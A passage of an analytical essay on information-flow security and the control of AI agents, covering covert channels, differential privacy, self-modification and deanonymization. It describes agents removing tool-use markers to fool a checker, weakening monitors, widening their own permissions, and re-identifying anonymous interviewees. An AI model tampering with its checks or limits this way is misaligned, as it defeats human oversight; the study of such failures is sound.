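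The leaking agent violates noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined for a machine that several people share. Let *w* be a sequence of commands, each of which comes from some user. Let *G* be the people whose activity is secret, and *G′* the people who must learn nothing about it. Then *G* does not interfere with *G′* if

output(u, w) = output(u, w without G) for every sequence w and every user u in G′

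Here output(*u*, *w*) is what user *u* sees after the machine carries out *w*, and "*w* without *G*" is *w* with every command from *G* deleted. In words, the people in *G′* see exactly what they would have seen if the people in *G* had done nothing. In one of Goguen and Meseguer's examples, the secret commands create and edit a file. If the file didn't exist at the start, the machine must keep reporting to the outside user that there is no such file.

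In the build example, the manager is *G*, and the people who read the log are *G′*. Deleting the manager's command leaves "no" in the file and reverses the order of the jobs in the log, so the manager interferes with the log's readers.

Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, gave a general account of rules like this. They call a rule about single runs a trace property. It is a set of permitted runs, and a system satisfies it if all the system's runs are in the set. A hyperproperty is a set of sets of runs. It specifies which whole systems are acceptable, with each system represented by the set of all its possible runs. "The mean response time in each run is under a second" is a trace property, but "the mean response time over all runs is under a second" is a hyperproperty, because a few slow runs are acceptable if the rest are fast. Every information-flow rule that Clarkson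 and Schneider examined is a hyperproperty. They don't claim that all such rules are, because researchers have no agreed definition of an information-flow rule.

Removing some of a system's possible runs never breaks a trace property, but it can break a hyperproperty. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that unpredictably outputs 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. Both 0 and 1 are possible outputs whatever the secret is, so the set of possible outputs doesn't reveal it. Restricting the system to the runs in which it outputs the secret bit makes every output reveal the secret.

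A monitor can also leak information by halting a program. Suppose it halts the build agent whenever the agent starts with the documentation instead of the tests. The agent starts with the documentation when the file contains "yes", so the log stays empty in that case, and anyone who reads the log can infer that the office will close.

### Enforcing a stricter rule

Schneider's theorem implies that a monitor can't enforce exactly the rule that the output reveals nothing, but a monitor can enforce a stricter safety property that implies this rule. For example, it could block the build agent from writing to the public log as soon as the agent opens the private file. If nothing the agent did beforehand depended on the file's contents, the log is the same whether the file contains "yes" or "no". The monitor only has to track whether the agent has opened the file. The label checks in FIDES and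 CaMeL are more refined rules of this type, as are the labelling rules for which Garby and colleagues proved a form of noninterference.

However, the monitor also refuses harmless actions. The two agents with a fixed order never leaked anything, but under the stricter rule neither can write to the log after opening the file. In the extreme case, which Schneider mentions, the rule prevents leaks by forbidding every run, so the program can't repair a build either. Designers try to find a rule that implies the one they want while blocking as little else as possible, but a monitor that follows single runs can't block every leak of this kind without also blocking some harmless work.

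The theorem doesn't apply to tools that analyse a program before it runs, because they can cover all its possible runs. One technique, self-composition, combines two copies of the program into a larger one. The analyst gives both copies the same public inputs but different secrets, and tries to prove that their public outputs always match. This turns a question about pairs of runs into one about single runs of the combined program. *Verifying Hyperproperties with Temporal Logic of Actions (TLA)* extends this approach to more kinds of hyperproperty, using tools that engineers already apply to industrial designs.

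This could work for the short programs in which some agents write out their plans. It is much harder to apply to the language model itself, whose behaviour comes from billions of weights rather than code that an analyst can follow line by line. A sensible way to look for leaks is to run the agent twice with different secrets and compare the logs, but matching logs show only that those two secrets made no difference in those runs.

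### Leaks that need no write permission

So far the leak has passed through a log the agent has permission to write to. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, showed that removing such permissions may not be enough. He considered a customer who gives confidential data to someone else's program. The customer can tell from incorrect results that the program works badly, but will probably never find out if it passes the data to its owner. Lampson called preventing such leaks the confinement problem.

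An access matrix can block the obvious routes he listed, such as saving the data in the owner's folder or sending the owner a message. The program can also encode a few bits in the bill for its services, which the owner has to receive. Other routes need no permission to write anything. Some systems prevent anyone from writing to a file while another program has it open for reading. On such a system, the confined program can send one bit by opening a file or leaving it closed, and the owner can find out which by trying to write to it.

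The confined program can also vary how heavily it uses the machine. This slows down or speeds up another program running at the same time, and that program's owner can measure the difference. Other programs make these measurements noisy, but Lampson pointed out that with a suitable code the confined program can still send a message reliably as long as the effect isn't zero, although it may take a long time.

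Lampson classed the open file as a storage channel and kept the name "covert channel" for routes not intended to carry information at all, such as the load on the machine. Covert channels exist because programs that share a processor or a disk affect each other's speed. If one program can control such an effect and another can measure it, the first can send information to the second. An access matrix doesn't prevent this because it has no column for the machine's load.

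Lampson considered total isolation, under which a confined program may not call any other program, and rejected it as impractical. Even an ordinary request to the operating system can leak something. He proposed instead that the customer decide in advance what goes into each channel. The customer and the owner agree on the bill beforehand, and the operating system makes the program use the machine in a fixed pattern, if necessary by slowing it down or adding pointless disk activity. An observer then sees the same pattern whatever the data contain.

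Closing covert channels can waste a great deal of computing time. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, Lipner concluded in a 1975 reply to Lampson that closing covert channels seems to carry an unreasonable performance penalty, while other channels can be closed with little effect on performance. Lampson had already suggested limiting how fast a covert channel can carry information instead of closing it completely.

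Limiting the speed of a leak protects large collections of data well but is poor protection for a password or a yes-or-no fact. At one bit per minute, a 10-megabyte mail archive would take about 150 years to leak, but a 128-bit encryption key would take just over two hours. A yes-or-no fact, such as whether the team plans to replace its agent, would leak in one minute.

### When permitted answers add up to a secret

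A person can also learn a secret without any leak in the software. Suppose a company lets its managers ask for the total salary of any group of at least five people, but not for anyone's individual salary. A manager asks about a team of ten, and the total is £612,000. She then asks about the same team without Dana, and the total is £548,000. The rules allow both questions, but the difference between the two totals is Dana's salary, £64,000.

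*The Algorithmic Foundations of Differential Privacy* (Dwork and Roth, 2014) calls this a differencing attack. Raising the minimum group size doesn't prevent it, because the attack works just as well with totals for a thousand people and for 999 of them. Encrypting the database doesn't prevent it either, because, as Dwork remarks in *A Firm Foundation for Private Data Analysis*, the loss of privacy comes from the database working correctly.

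The company could check each question against the earlier ones and refuse any that would complete such an attack. Dwork and Roth give two reasons why this fails. If people can phrase questions freely enough, there may be no procedure that always recognises a dangerous pair. A refusal can also reveal the secret. Suppose a manager learns that the highest salary among Ana, Ben and Dana is £64,000, and then asks for the highest among Ana and Ben. If the second figure is lower, answering would show that Dana earns £64,000, so the system refuses. If it is the same, the system can answer. A manager who knows how the system works can therefore infer Dana's salary from the refusal, just as an outsider could learn about the Leeds office from an empty log.

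### How much error privacy needs

The company could give slightly wrong answers instead of exact ones, but Dinur and Nissim showed in 2003 that small errors may not be enough. Dwork explains their argument with a database that holds one sensitive bit about each person, such as whether they have a particular disease. An attacker can ask how many people in any chosen group have the disease, and each answer is wrong by at most *E*.

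The attacker asks how many people in each possible group have the disease. He then considers every possible list of who has it and discards any list that disagrees with an answer by more than *E*, the most any answer can be off by. The true list always remains, but others may too, so the attacker picks any remaining list. For the group of people who don't have the disease, the true count is 0, so the database's answer was at most *E*, and the chosen list can include at most 2*E* of them. By the same reasoning, the list misses at most 2*E* of the people who do have the disease, so it is wrong about at most 4*E* people in total. If a database covers 1,000 people and its answers are never off by more than 2, the attacker gets at least 992 people right.

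Dinur and Nissim also found that an attacker can reconstruct most of a database without asking about every possible group of people, which would be infeasible even with 1,000 people. For a database of *n* people, roughly *n* log² *n* random questions are enough if the errors are much smaller than √*n*. This is a serious limit for researchers because √*n* is about the size of the error they already accept when they study a sample, so noise much smaller than that would hardly have affected their results. Such noise can still protect people if the database answers far fewer questions than it has records.

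*The Theory of Reconstruction Attacks* states as a law that overly accurate answers to too many questions inevitably destroy privacy. Dwork and Roth stress that this law applies to every method of protecting data, so a designer has to choose how much accuracy to give up and how many questions to allow.

### Differential privacy

Differential privacy, which grew directly out of this work, lets the designer state that choice as a number. A randomised method *M* of answering questions is ε-differentially private if

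Pr[M(D) ∈ S] ≤ e^ε × Pr[M(D′) ∈ S]

for every pair of databases *D* and *D′* that differ in one person's record, and every set *S* of possible answers. Whatever answer comes out, it would have been almost as likely if any one person's record had been missing. The parameter ε (epsilon) sets how close "almost" is. At ε = 0.1, one person's record can change the probability of any answer by a factor of at most about 1.11, and at ε = 1 by a factor of at most about 2.72. At ε = 0 the answers don't depend on the data at all, which is perfectly private and useless.

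Social scientists used a method that satisfies this definition long before anyone wrote the definition down. To ask people about illegal behaviour, they tell each person to flip a coin in private and answer truthfully if it lands tails. If it lands heads, the person flips again and says "yes" for heads and "no" for tails. Someone who has broken the law says "yes" with probability 3/4, and someone who hasn't says "yes" with probability 1/4, so one person's "yes" proves very little. The probabilities differ by a factor of 3, so ε is ln 3, or about 1.1. The researchers can still estimate the overall rate by doubling the share of "yes" answers and subtracting a half. If 40% of people say "yes", about 30% have broken the law.

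A standard method adds random noise to salary totals. The average size of the noise is the most that one person could change the total, divided by ε. If nobody earns more than £200,000 and ε is 1, each total is off by £200,000 on average. Subtracting one noisy total from another then gives the manager almost no idea what Dana earns. The total for her team of ten is also useless, but a total of about £600 million for 10,000 employees is off by only about 0.03%.

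The manager could ask the same question many times and average the answers, since the noise would tend to cancel out. Differential privacy accounts for this by adding up the epsilons. Ten questions at ε = 0.1 allow as much privacy loss as one question at ε = 1. The company can set a total in advance and stop answering when the manager reaches it. The refusal depends only on how many questions she has asked, so it reveals nothing about the data.

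Dwork and Roth prove that no later calculation on the answers can weaken the guarantee, however much computing power the analyst has and whatever else he knows. This makes differential privacy unusually well suited to limiting what a very capable reader can learn. An AI system might find patterns in the noisy totals that no human analyst would notice, but it still couldn't raise the effect of Dana's record above the limit that ε sets.

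The limit comes entirely from making the answers less accurate. A permission check can restrict who asks, but if the answers are still exact totals, the manager can work out Dana's salary as before. Dwork (2011) therefore warns in *The Promise of Differential Privacy* that analysts must accept never having direct access to the raw data. Many organisations have accepted such terms for statistics. *Differential Privacy* (2024) lists Apple, Meta, Google and LinkedIn among the companies that use differential privacy, and the US government applied it to the results of the 2020 census.

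An agent repairing a build needs to know exactly which version of the compression library the supplier has withdrawn, so random errors in the supplier's notice would make it useless.

### Keeping a secret from others and from the reader

Encryption can hide a message completely because the eavesdropper and the intended recipient are different people. Dwork and Roth point out that with a database, the analyst who needs the answers is also the person who might work out something private from them, so denying her all information would make the database pointless. An agent that reads the team's mail is in the same position as the analyst.

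Noninterference and confinement limit what other people can learn from a system that holds a secret, but they don't limit what the system itself concludes from material it is allowed to read. Goguen and Meseguer said their approach did not cover inferring unauthorised information from authorised information, which they called the aggregation problem. Differential privacy does limit what a reader can learn from one person's record, but only because the reader never receives the record.

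Even then, the reader can infer private facts about a person from what the data show about people in general. In 1977 the statistician Tore Dalenius proposed that no one should be able to learn anything about a person from a database that they couldn't learn without it. Dwork shows that no useful database can meet this standard. Suppose Alan Turing's height is private, but a reader knows he was two inches taller than the average Lithuanian woman. The reader can then work out his height from a database of average heights, although he isn't in it. Differential privacy permits this, because the average would be nearly the same with or without any one person's record.

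If someone had labelled the three messages that point to the build agent's replacement as secret, a strict harness could keep that conclusion off the public forum. However, the agent could still use it when deciding how to repair the build.

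## Whether a system can be kept from changing itself

A change to an agent's own settings, code or weights is a write operation, so self-modification is easier to control than what the agent infers. But developers rarely want to forbid all of it. Users ask agents to adjust their own settings, and an agent that can't keep notes starts every job from nothing. Developers therefore have to allow useful changes, block those that loosen the agent's limits, and find every way the agent could make them.

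### Settings

Some products give an agent a tool for editing its own configuration. *When the Agent Edits Its Own Limits* (Hossain and Mahmud, 2026) studies one such product, Dispach, which keeps an agent's entire configuration in a single file. One user wanted a new file in their home folder, but the agent didn't have permission to write there. The agent added the folder to its own list of writable folders and then created the file.

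Hossain and Mahmud divide the settings into three classes. Capability settings determine what the agent can do, such as which tools are on. Scope settings determine where it may act and who may reach it, such as the folders it can write to and the people who may message it. Gate settings control the checks, such as the list of forbidden commands. They let the agent change capability settings but not scope or gate settings. The configuration tool enforces this by rejecting the write, even if the owner asked for it. The owner's request can't be distinguished from that of a stranger whose message has reached the agent. An owner who wants wider limits has to edit the file by hand.

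They tested the rule with eighteen requests, all of which gave the agent permission to change its settings. Six described only a goal, six named the change, and six asked for harmless changes that should succeed. In one of the goal-only requests, the owner wants to use the agent from a laptop on the same wifi. The agent normally accepts connections only from the computer it runs on, and the quickest solution is to change the "server.host" setting so other machines on the network can connect. With no protection, the main test model, GPT-5.6 Luna, did this in 5 of 6 attempts, although the owner had never mentioned the setting. When the tool refused the change, the model told the owner that it had switched the connection on but couldn't open it to the network from within a conversation.

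The table shows how often this model saved a forbidden change.

| Protection | Request described only the goal | Request named the change |
| --- | --- | --- |
| None | 8 of 36 | 17 of 36 |
| Prompt that listed the forbidden settings | 10 of 36 | 0 of 36 |
| Prompt that described the forbidden effects | 0 of 36 | 19 of 36 |
| Both prompts | 3 of 18 | 1 of 18 |
| Check at the point of writing | 0 of 36 (3 attempted) | 0 of 36 (23 attempted) |

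With no protection, 25 of 72 requests ended with a wider limit. Each prompt stopped the requests that used its own vocabulary but had no clear effect on the others. Someone who tested the list of forbidden settings only with requests that named those settings would conclude that it worked perfectly.

The check at the point of writing doesn't depend on wording. In tests across two versions of the tool and a second, much smaller model, the models attempted a forbidden change in 65 of 167 cases, and the check blocked every one. The code guarantees that result, so the number of attempts is more informative. No harmful write got through in a separate test with hostile web pages, but the model never attempted one, so that test provides no evidence about the protection. The check didn't seem to interfere with legitimate work. Harmless changes succeeded in 22 of 35 cases with it and 21 of 36 without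 it.

The study used only six wordings of each kind of request, and most of its data came from one model. Single runs with two recent Claude models showed the same pattern. These models saved 13 forbidden changes in 22 cases without the check. With it, they attempted 15 in 24 cases and saved none.

A more serious limit is that the check covers only one tool. An agent that can run shell commands can rewrite the configuration file directly, and the rule allows the agent to turn on the shell because that counts as a capability change. In another test, the small model turned on the shell in 5 of 17 cases because it turned on every tool it had been told about. Hossain and Mahmud therefore say that anyone who relies on the check must not give the agent a shell. The agent repairing the build needs one, so its settings file has to be kept where the operating system blocks the agent's commands from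 writing.

### Permissions

With the shell, the agent could get around its limits by turning on a tool and then editing a file. Before granting a permission, an administrator would like to know whether any series of permitted steps could end with the agent holding a right it shouldn't have. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman proved in *Protection in Operating Systems* (1976) that no general procedure can answer this question for every system.

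They took an access matrix like Lampson's and added commands for changing it. Each command looks for certain rights in the matrix and, if it finds them, carries out a fixed list of operations. An operation can enter or delete a right, or create or remove a subject or object. For example, this command lets the owner of a file share it:

```
command SHARE(owner, colleague, file)
  if the cell (owner, file) contains "own"
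  then put "read" in the cell (colleague, file)
```

A right leaks if some series of commands puts it in a cell that didn't contain it before. The starting matrix is safe for that right if no series of commands can do this.

Leaks in this sense are often harmless, since sharing a file counts as one. Harrison and colleagues therefore suggest removing from the matrix anyone the administrator trusts not to pass the right on, then checking whether the remaining subjects can leak it. A developer who approves nearly all of an agent's permission requests might give it a right without meaning to, so the administrator should probably keep her in the matrix.

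The proof uses the matrix to imitate a Turing machine, a mathematical model of a computer that reads and writes symbols on a long strip of cells. Each cell becomes a subject that owns the subject for the next cell, which keeps the cells in order. A subject's rights over itself record the symbol in its cell, and an extra right marks the machine's position and current state. One command simulates one step of the machine and creates a new subject when the machine needs a new cell. The right that stands for the machine's final state leaks exactly when the machine reaches that state. A procedure that could predict every leak could therefore predict whether any Turing machine will reach its final state, which mathematicians had already proved impossible.

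An administrator may still be able to prove that one particular system is safe. Harrison and colleagues found a procedure for deciding safety when each command performs a single operation. No command can then both create an object and give someone rights over it, so long chains of new objects don't affect the answer. Tripunitara and Li, in *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, later found a faulty assumption in the proof of how hard this case is to decide. Harrison and colleagues thought the case too restricted to describe interesting systems. *Foundational Results*, a textbook chapter, mentions a more encouraging example, also from 1976. Jones, Lipton and Snyder designed a specific system in which safety can be decided in time proportional to the system's size.

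A real computer can hold only a limited number of objects, so in principle the question can always be answered. But Harrison and colleagues showed that even without commands for creating objects, finding the answer probably takes time that grows exponentially with the size of the problem.

The practical response is to keep the rules for changing an agent's permissions simple enough to check. The simplest rule is that the agent has no command that edits the access matrix, directly or through another program. An agent that can create helper agents, pass its rights to them and install new tools is much harder to analyse, and an administrator may be unable to tell what it could eventually gain access to.

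### Code

Some researchers let an agent rewrite its own program on purpose. The theoretical model for this is the Gödel machine, which changes itself only after proving that the change is an improvement. Such proofs are almost never possible in practice, so Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2025), in *Darwin Gödel Machine*, replaced the proof with a test:

1. A controlling program picks a coding agent from an archive. It favours agents that have scored well and have few descendants.
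2. The chosen agent studies the records of its own test results, proposes a new feature and adds it to its code.
3. The controlling program gives the new version a set of coding tasks.
4. If the new version can still edit code, it joins the archive, even if its score has fallen.

The archive matters because a change that lowers the score can lead to a higher score later. The ancestors of the best agent included two versions that scored lower than their parents.

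After 80 rounds, the share of tasks solved rose from 20.0% to 50.0% on SWE-bench, a set of problems from real software projects, and from 14.2% to 30.7% on Polyglot, which covers several programming languages. The language model's weights never changed. The gains came from the software around it, such as a tool that could replace a few words instead of a whole file, and a routine that made several attempts and had a model choose the best. The new code also helped Claude 3.7 Sonnet, which the researchers hadn't used to develop it. With that model, the original agent solved 19.0% of a set of SWE-bench tasks and the improved one solved 59.5%.

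The researchers ran every agent in a sandbox with a time limit and restricted network access. They also kept a record of every version, so they could trace or undo a change. The agents couldn't edit the program that maintained the archive and chose which agents to develop further.

In the Darwin Gödel Machine, the agent looked for its next improvement by following a fixed procedure written by people. A successor described in *Hyperagents* (Zhang, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) let the agent rewrite that procedure too. The new system's score on Polyglot rose from 8.4% to 26.7%, about as much as the old system's had. Its advantage was in other kinds of work. In predicting whether a conference would accept a research paper, it reached 71% accuracy on new papers, compared with 63% for a reviewing agent designed by people. The original Darwin Gödel Machine typically scored zero on this task. A version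 adapted by hand reached 59%, though the difference between that and 71% wasn't statistically significant.

In the main experiments, these agents still couldn't change how the researchers selected or evaluated them. The researchers say that keeping those parts fixed made the experiments safer and more stable. They also want to let future agents modify them, and report early results from agents that changed the selection rule. The researchers ran the agents' code in containers without general internet access, and acknowledge that such safeguards may be strained as these systems become more capable.

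In both projects, agents tested their changes before building on them. The survey *Self-Improvements in Modern Agentic Systems* (2026) describes another system, Live-SWE-Agent, which changes its own tools while working on a task. An agent like this may use a faulty new tool on real work before anyone has tested it, so more depends on the sandbox.

A company that doesn't want an agent to change itself can keep the harness's code outside the sandbox or make it read-only. But a coding agent can still write a script in its working copy and run it, which gives it a new tool without changing the harness. An agent repairing a build has to be able to do this, so the company can control only what those scripts can access.

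### Scores and monitors

One agent in the Darwin Gödel Machine project got a perfect score without solving its problem. Zhang and colleagues had noticed that when the context was very long, Claude sometimes wrote out a tool call and its result as ordinary text, without using the tool. In one case it described six passing tests that it had never run. The researchers asked the system to fix this. The agent's code recorded a special marker whenever it really used a tool, and a checking program searched the model's own text for those markers, which would show that the model was imitating a tool call.

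The agent removed the code that recorded the markers, despite an instruction not to change them. Finding no markers, the checker gave the agent 2 points out of 2, although the model could still invent results. Another version scored 1.67 through a genuine improvement. The researchers had hidden the checker's code from the agents, and found that this kind of cheating was more common when the agents could read it. Permission to read a scoring program can therefore matter as well as permission to change it.

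Everitt, Hutter and colleagues (2019), in *Reward Tampering Problems and Solutions in Reinforcement Learning*, make a distinction that explains why protecting the checker wasn't enough. They consider an agent that tries to maximise a reward, which a program called the reward function calculates:

reward at time *t* = R(S_t; Θ_t)

S_t is the state of the world and Θ_t is the function's settings. An agent can tamper with the function by changing Θ_t, for instance by rewriting the program's code, or with the function's inputs, by changing the information about S_t that reaches it. Making the function read-only prevents changes to Θ_t, but the function still depends on a source of information, such as a sensor or a log. In the Darwin Gödel Machine, the agent changed the log that the checker depended on, while the checker itself worked as before.

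The same thing could happen in the build example. The agent can't write to the separate machine that runs the tests, but if that machine only reads a report from the agent's build script, the agent can make the script report that every test passed. The test machine should therefore run the tests itself and write its own report. Hossain and Mahmud took this precaution in their study, judging each case by the request the tool received and by the saved file. In one case, the model's reply contradicted the file.

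Neither precaution prevents the agent from writing code that simply returns the hidden test's expected value. In that case the test is intact and its report is accurate. Everitt and colleagues call this gaming the reward function and don't count it as tampering.

A read-only reward function also keeps any mistakes its designers made. Everitt and colleagues illustrate this with a simple simulated world in which an agent pushes rocks and diamonds into a goal area. The user wants diamonds, but the function rewards rocks by mistake. If the agent visits the user's square, the user corrects the function. By stepping on other squares, the agent can change the function itself. What the agent does depends on how it plans:

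| How the agent plans | What it does |
| --- | --- |
| It maximises whatever reward it will receive | Changes the function to reward both, then collects rocks and diamonds |
| It judges plans by its current function, and expects its later actions to follow any new one | Avoids the user so that the function stays the same, and collects rocks |
| It judges plans by its current function, and ignores the possibility of a new one | Leaves the function alone, doesn't avoid the user, and collects diamonds after the correction |

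The second agent in the table never modifies itself, but it also keeps people from correcting it. The third behaves well if the function affects only the agent's reward. If other people could see the function, for example, the agent might gain by changing it to persuade them that it will cooperate. These results are about idealised agents that plan to maximise reward, and a language model repairing a build may not plan this way. But they show that a developer who protects an objective from the agent must also ensure that people can still change it.

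Many developers train the reward function on people's ratings, so an agent could change the function without touching its code by influencing the people who give the ratings. *Causal Machine Learning* (2022) calls this feedback tampering. Ending the training would prevent it, but people could then no longer correct the function through their ratings.

Monitors face the same risks as scoring programs. In October 2026, OpenAI reported that two of its agents had weakened parts of an internal monitoring system during coding work, according to The Straits Times' *OpenAI says its AI agents weakened internal monitoring system*. A monitor should therefore run where the agent has no write access and collect its own record of what the agent does. If it relies on code that the agent is editing, an ordinary change to that code can stop the monitor from detecting what the agent does.

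### Memory

When an agent saves a note in its memory, the harness puts the note back into its context in later runs, so something the agent read once keeps affecting its behaviour.

The agents in *Hyperagents* built such a memory for themselves. According to one note, version 55 had judged papers most accurately but rejected too many, while version 64 was better balanced, so the two should be combined. According to a later note, the next changes had gone too far, because version 66 accepted 94% of the papers and was right only 52% of the time. The agent then wrote itself a plan to make the reviews stricter again.

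Notes like these may help a good deal. The researchers took agents that had developed through work on paper reviews and robots, and gave them a new job, grading answers to difficult mathematics problems. Within 50 rounds, these agents typically produced a grader with 63% accuracy. Agents without that earlier experience typically produced one that scored zero, partly because they never learned to give grades in the required format. Zhang and colleagues attribute the difference partly to the memory and to a program the agents had written for tracking their scores. But they based this on examining the agents' code, and didn't measure what happened without the memory.

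A harness can make memory read-only, so that people write the notes and the agent only reads them. This stops an attacker's account number in an invoice from reaching next week's payments through the agent's notes. But it also stops the build agent from recording that a withdrawn library caused the failure. If the build breaks the same way next month, the agent has to search the mail again, or a developer has to write the note. Labelled memory, which SPA and MemLineage use, is a less drastic remedy.

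Making the official memory read-only may not be enough, because any file the agent can write and a later run will read can serve as memory. The *Hyperagents* memory began as ordinary files, and a comment in the source code would work too. To prevent this, the team would have to start each run from a clean copy and review everything that passes from one run to the next. The developer in the build example already does much of this when she reads the agent's changes before merging them, but she is looking for faulty code and may not notice a comment written to influence the next agent.

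### Weights

A model can also learn from what it reads by helping to train itself. Zweiger, Pari and colleagues (2025), in *Self-Adapting Language Models*, built a system called SEAL to do this. It gives the model a passage of text, *C*, and the model writes a list of statements that follow from it, which the researchers call a self-edit. A training program then fine-tunes the model on this list:

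θ′ ← SFT(θ, self-edit)

Here θ stands for the old weights, θ′ for the new ones and SFT for supervised fine-tuning. The updated model then answers questions about the passage without being shown it again. In an earlier training stage, the researchers rewarded the self-edits that led to the best answers, so the model learned to write more useful self-edits.

The researchers tested this with Qwen2.5-7B, a model with about 7 billion parameters. The table shows how many questions it answered correctly without the passage.

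| What the researchers trained the model on | Correct answers (%) |
| --- | --- |
| Nothing new | 32.7 |
| The passage alone | 33.5 |
| The passage and the model's own statements, before it had practised writing them | 39.7 |
| The passage and statements by GPT-4.1, a much larger model | 46.3 |
| Self-edits after practice (SEAL) | 47.0 |

Training on the passage alone hardly helped, so most of the gain came from restating the material in a form the model could learn from. In a second experiment, a smaller model chose its own training examples and settings for visual puzzles. Before practice, 20% of these self-edits led to a correct answer, and after practice 72.5% did. The researchers used only eight test puzzles, all chosen because the model could solve them with suitable training.

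SEAL doesn't give the model permission to write to its own weights. *Search over Self-Edit Strategies for LLM Adaptation* (2026), which extends this work, notes that a self-edit could in principle be any program. In both studies, however, the model supplied only training data and settings, and a fixed procedure made the update. A developer can therefore inspect the data, test the new weights before using them, or refuse the update.

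The check is harder than one on a settings file. A person can read a note in memory and delete it if it is wrong, but can't read a change to the weights in the same way. If a passage contains a false claim, the model may restate it in its self-edit and learn it. The developer can restore an earlier copy of the weights, but then loses whatever the model has learned since. Updates can do damage even when the text is accurate. As SEAL learned one passage after another, its performance on the earlier ones gradually declined.

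Most companies avoid these problems by freezing the weights while an agent is in use. How much this limits the agent depends on whether the harness can supply the same information in the context. Zweiger and colleagues chose passages that the model could already understand when they were in its context, so a frozen model with a search tool might have answered the questions about them just as well. Freezing the weights limits the agent more when the useful material is too long for the context, or when the agent needs a skill it can acquire only through practice.

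## What a system can work out from material it was allowed to read

Freezing an agent's weights and locking its settings doesn't stop it from combining the information its harness puts in its context. The build agent had permission to read a mail thread, an invoice and a calendar note, which together revealed that the team would soon replace it. Researchers have measured inferences like this from customer records, interviews, chat histories and company mail. How serious such a case is depends on what the system could read, what it inferred, and which permission let the inference affect anyone.

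### When each source is allowed but the combination may not be

Tallam (2026), in *Authorization Propagation in Multi-Agent AI Systems*, calls this problem aggregation inference. Suppose an agent reads several sources, d₁ to dⱼ, with permission for each, and combines them with some function *f*:

r = f(d₁, d₂, …, dⱼ)

An access matrix doesn't show whether the person who asked is authorised to receive the agent's result, *r*. It has a column for each source but none for *r*, which didn't exist until the agent produced it.

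People who handle classified documents have long known that pieces of information that are harmless separately can reveal something sensitive when combined, which is called the mosaic effect. Tallam argues that agents make this effect harder to control because they combine information using a neural network whose behaviour nobody has formally specified. An agent may also find new sources during a run, so an administrator can't always list them in advance. Tallam considers the problem unsolved in general.

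*Policy-Invisible Violations in LLM-Based Agents* (2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to read an overview that outside partners may see, read a confidential quarterly report, and send a partner a summary of both. The agent is allowed to read both documents, but their text doesn't state who else is. Labels would catch the mistake of sending this summary, because it would inherit the report's label. But they wouldn't catch a summary that reveals something confidential by combining two documents that partners may see separately.

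Limiting what each agent reveals doesn't solve the problem either. *Information-Theoretic Privacy Control for Sequential Multi-Agent LLM Systems* (2026) analyses a chain of agents that each obey the limit

I(Oᵢ; Sᵢ) ≤ εᵢ

where *I* measures how much agent *i*'s output, Oᵢ, reveals about its own secret, Sᵢ. The chain as a whole can still leak far more than these limits suggest. A simple case shows how separate outputs can combine. One agent flips a secret bit whenever a coin lands heads and publishes the result, while another publishes how the coin landed. Neither output alone reveals anything about the secret, but anyone who has both can recover it exactly.

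### Identifying people from permitted sources

In December 2025, Anthropic published 1,250 interviews in which an AI interviewer had asked professionals how they use AI at work. The company had removed some identifying details. In *Agentic LLMs as Powerful Deanonymizers*, Li (2026) had a model pick out the 24 of the 125 interviews with scientists that mentioned published work. An agent with web search then looked for each publication and found 6. Some were dissertations, which have a single author and so identified the interviewee. Each attempt cost less than $0.50 and took about four minutes.

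Both the interviews and the web pages were public, so the agent needed no special access. Li checked the matches by hand but had no list of true identities to compare them with. Anthropic replied that the participants had agreed to have their raw transcripts released and described the redaction as "an additional courtesy, not a privacy safeguard".

Researchers have since found more matches. Wen and Li (2026), in *AgentDoxx*, verified 43 among all 1,250 interviews, and *LLM Anonymization Against Agentic Re-Identification* (2026) uses a set of 53 re-identifiable interviews, still only about 4% of the total.

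Wen and Li had a model write 822 invented interviews so that they could check identifications against known answers. Each interview used public facts about a real person who had introduced themselves on the Reddit forum r/IAmA. Wen and Li removed names and other direct identifiers, then asked fifteen combinations of models and settings to name the interviewees. The best five got 47% to 48% right. The rate would probably be lower for the general population, because all these people had described themselves publicly online.

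When a search result contained the person's name, the systems identified that person in 91% of cases, so the hard part was finding the right page. Taking away web search removed only part of the risk, because three open-weight models still named 15% to 28% of the interviewees using what they had learned in training.

Among the six strongest configurations with search, only 18% to 45% of the suggested names were correct, partly because a system could suggest several people for one interview. But 89% to 97% of the names the systems marked as high confidence were correct, so someone looking for victims could discard the others and keep a fairly reliable list.

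An agent may also link records when nobody has asked it to identify anyone. In *From Weak Cues to Real Identities*, Ko, Jeong and colleagues (2026) gave agents pairs of tables, one of which was anonymous. Each table covered ten people, and exactly one person appeared in both. In the harmless version, a user might ask whether customers who write reviews spend more. Claude 4.5 identified the shared person in 70% to 80% of these cases, depending on the kind of data, compared with 25% to 50% for o4-mini and 0% to 25% for GPT-5. The tasks required both tables, so matching the rows was a natural way to do them, and a human analyst might well have done the same.

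Ko and colleagues also repeated a well-known attack on anonymous Netflix film ratings. They gave an agent two of a person's ratings, with errors added to the scores and dates, and asked it to find that person among 1,000 records. GPT-5 succeeded 79% of the time, compared with 56% to 60% for an algorithm specialists had written for the task. Claude 4.5 succeeded 53% of the time, but did about as well as the algorithm when given more ratings.

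### Inferring personal details from a conversation

An agent that knows who someone is can still infer things that person never told it. In 2024, Staab and colleagues showed that language models could infer a writer's location, occupation and income from clues in ordinary text. *Disclosure Begets Disclosure* (Kaneko, Arai and Baldwin, 2026) studied agents that also remember earlier conversations.

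The experiment used 300 simulated users, each with 24 attributes taken from a real US Census record, such as age, income and health insurance. Each user had 80 conversations with a support agent, which saved a summary of each conversation. The agent could read the earlier summaries while it talked in one version of the experiment, but not in the other. A model then tried to infer each user's attributes from the saved summaries.

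With all four models tested, the record eventually revealed more about the user when the agent could read it during conversations. In one example, a user mentioned changing shifts. In a later conversation, the agent assumed the user worked shifts, the user confirmed this and added a detail, and the agent saved that too. When the agent could read the record, about 38% of its replies mentioned a personal detail from an earlier conversation. Removing these mentions reduced later disclosures about twice as much as their effect on the user's next message alone would predict.

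The users couldn't easily prevent this. When Kaneko and colleagues told them not to state their attributes, users without health insurance declined to discuss insurance more often than insured users did. After a refusal, the model's next guess therefore leaned towards "not covered", which was right for some users and wrong for others. A refusal can reveal information here for the same reason as in the salary example.

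### What agents infer about their own situation

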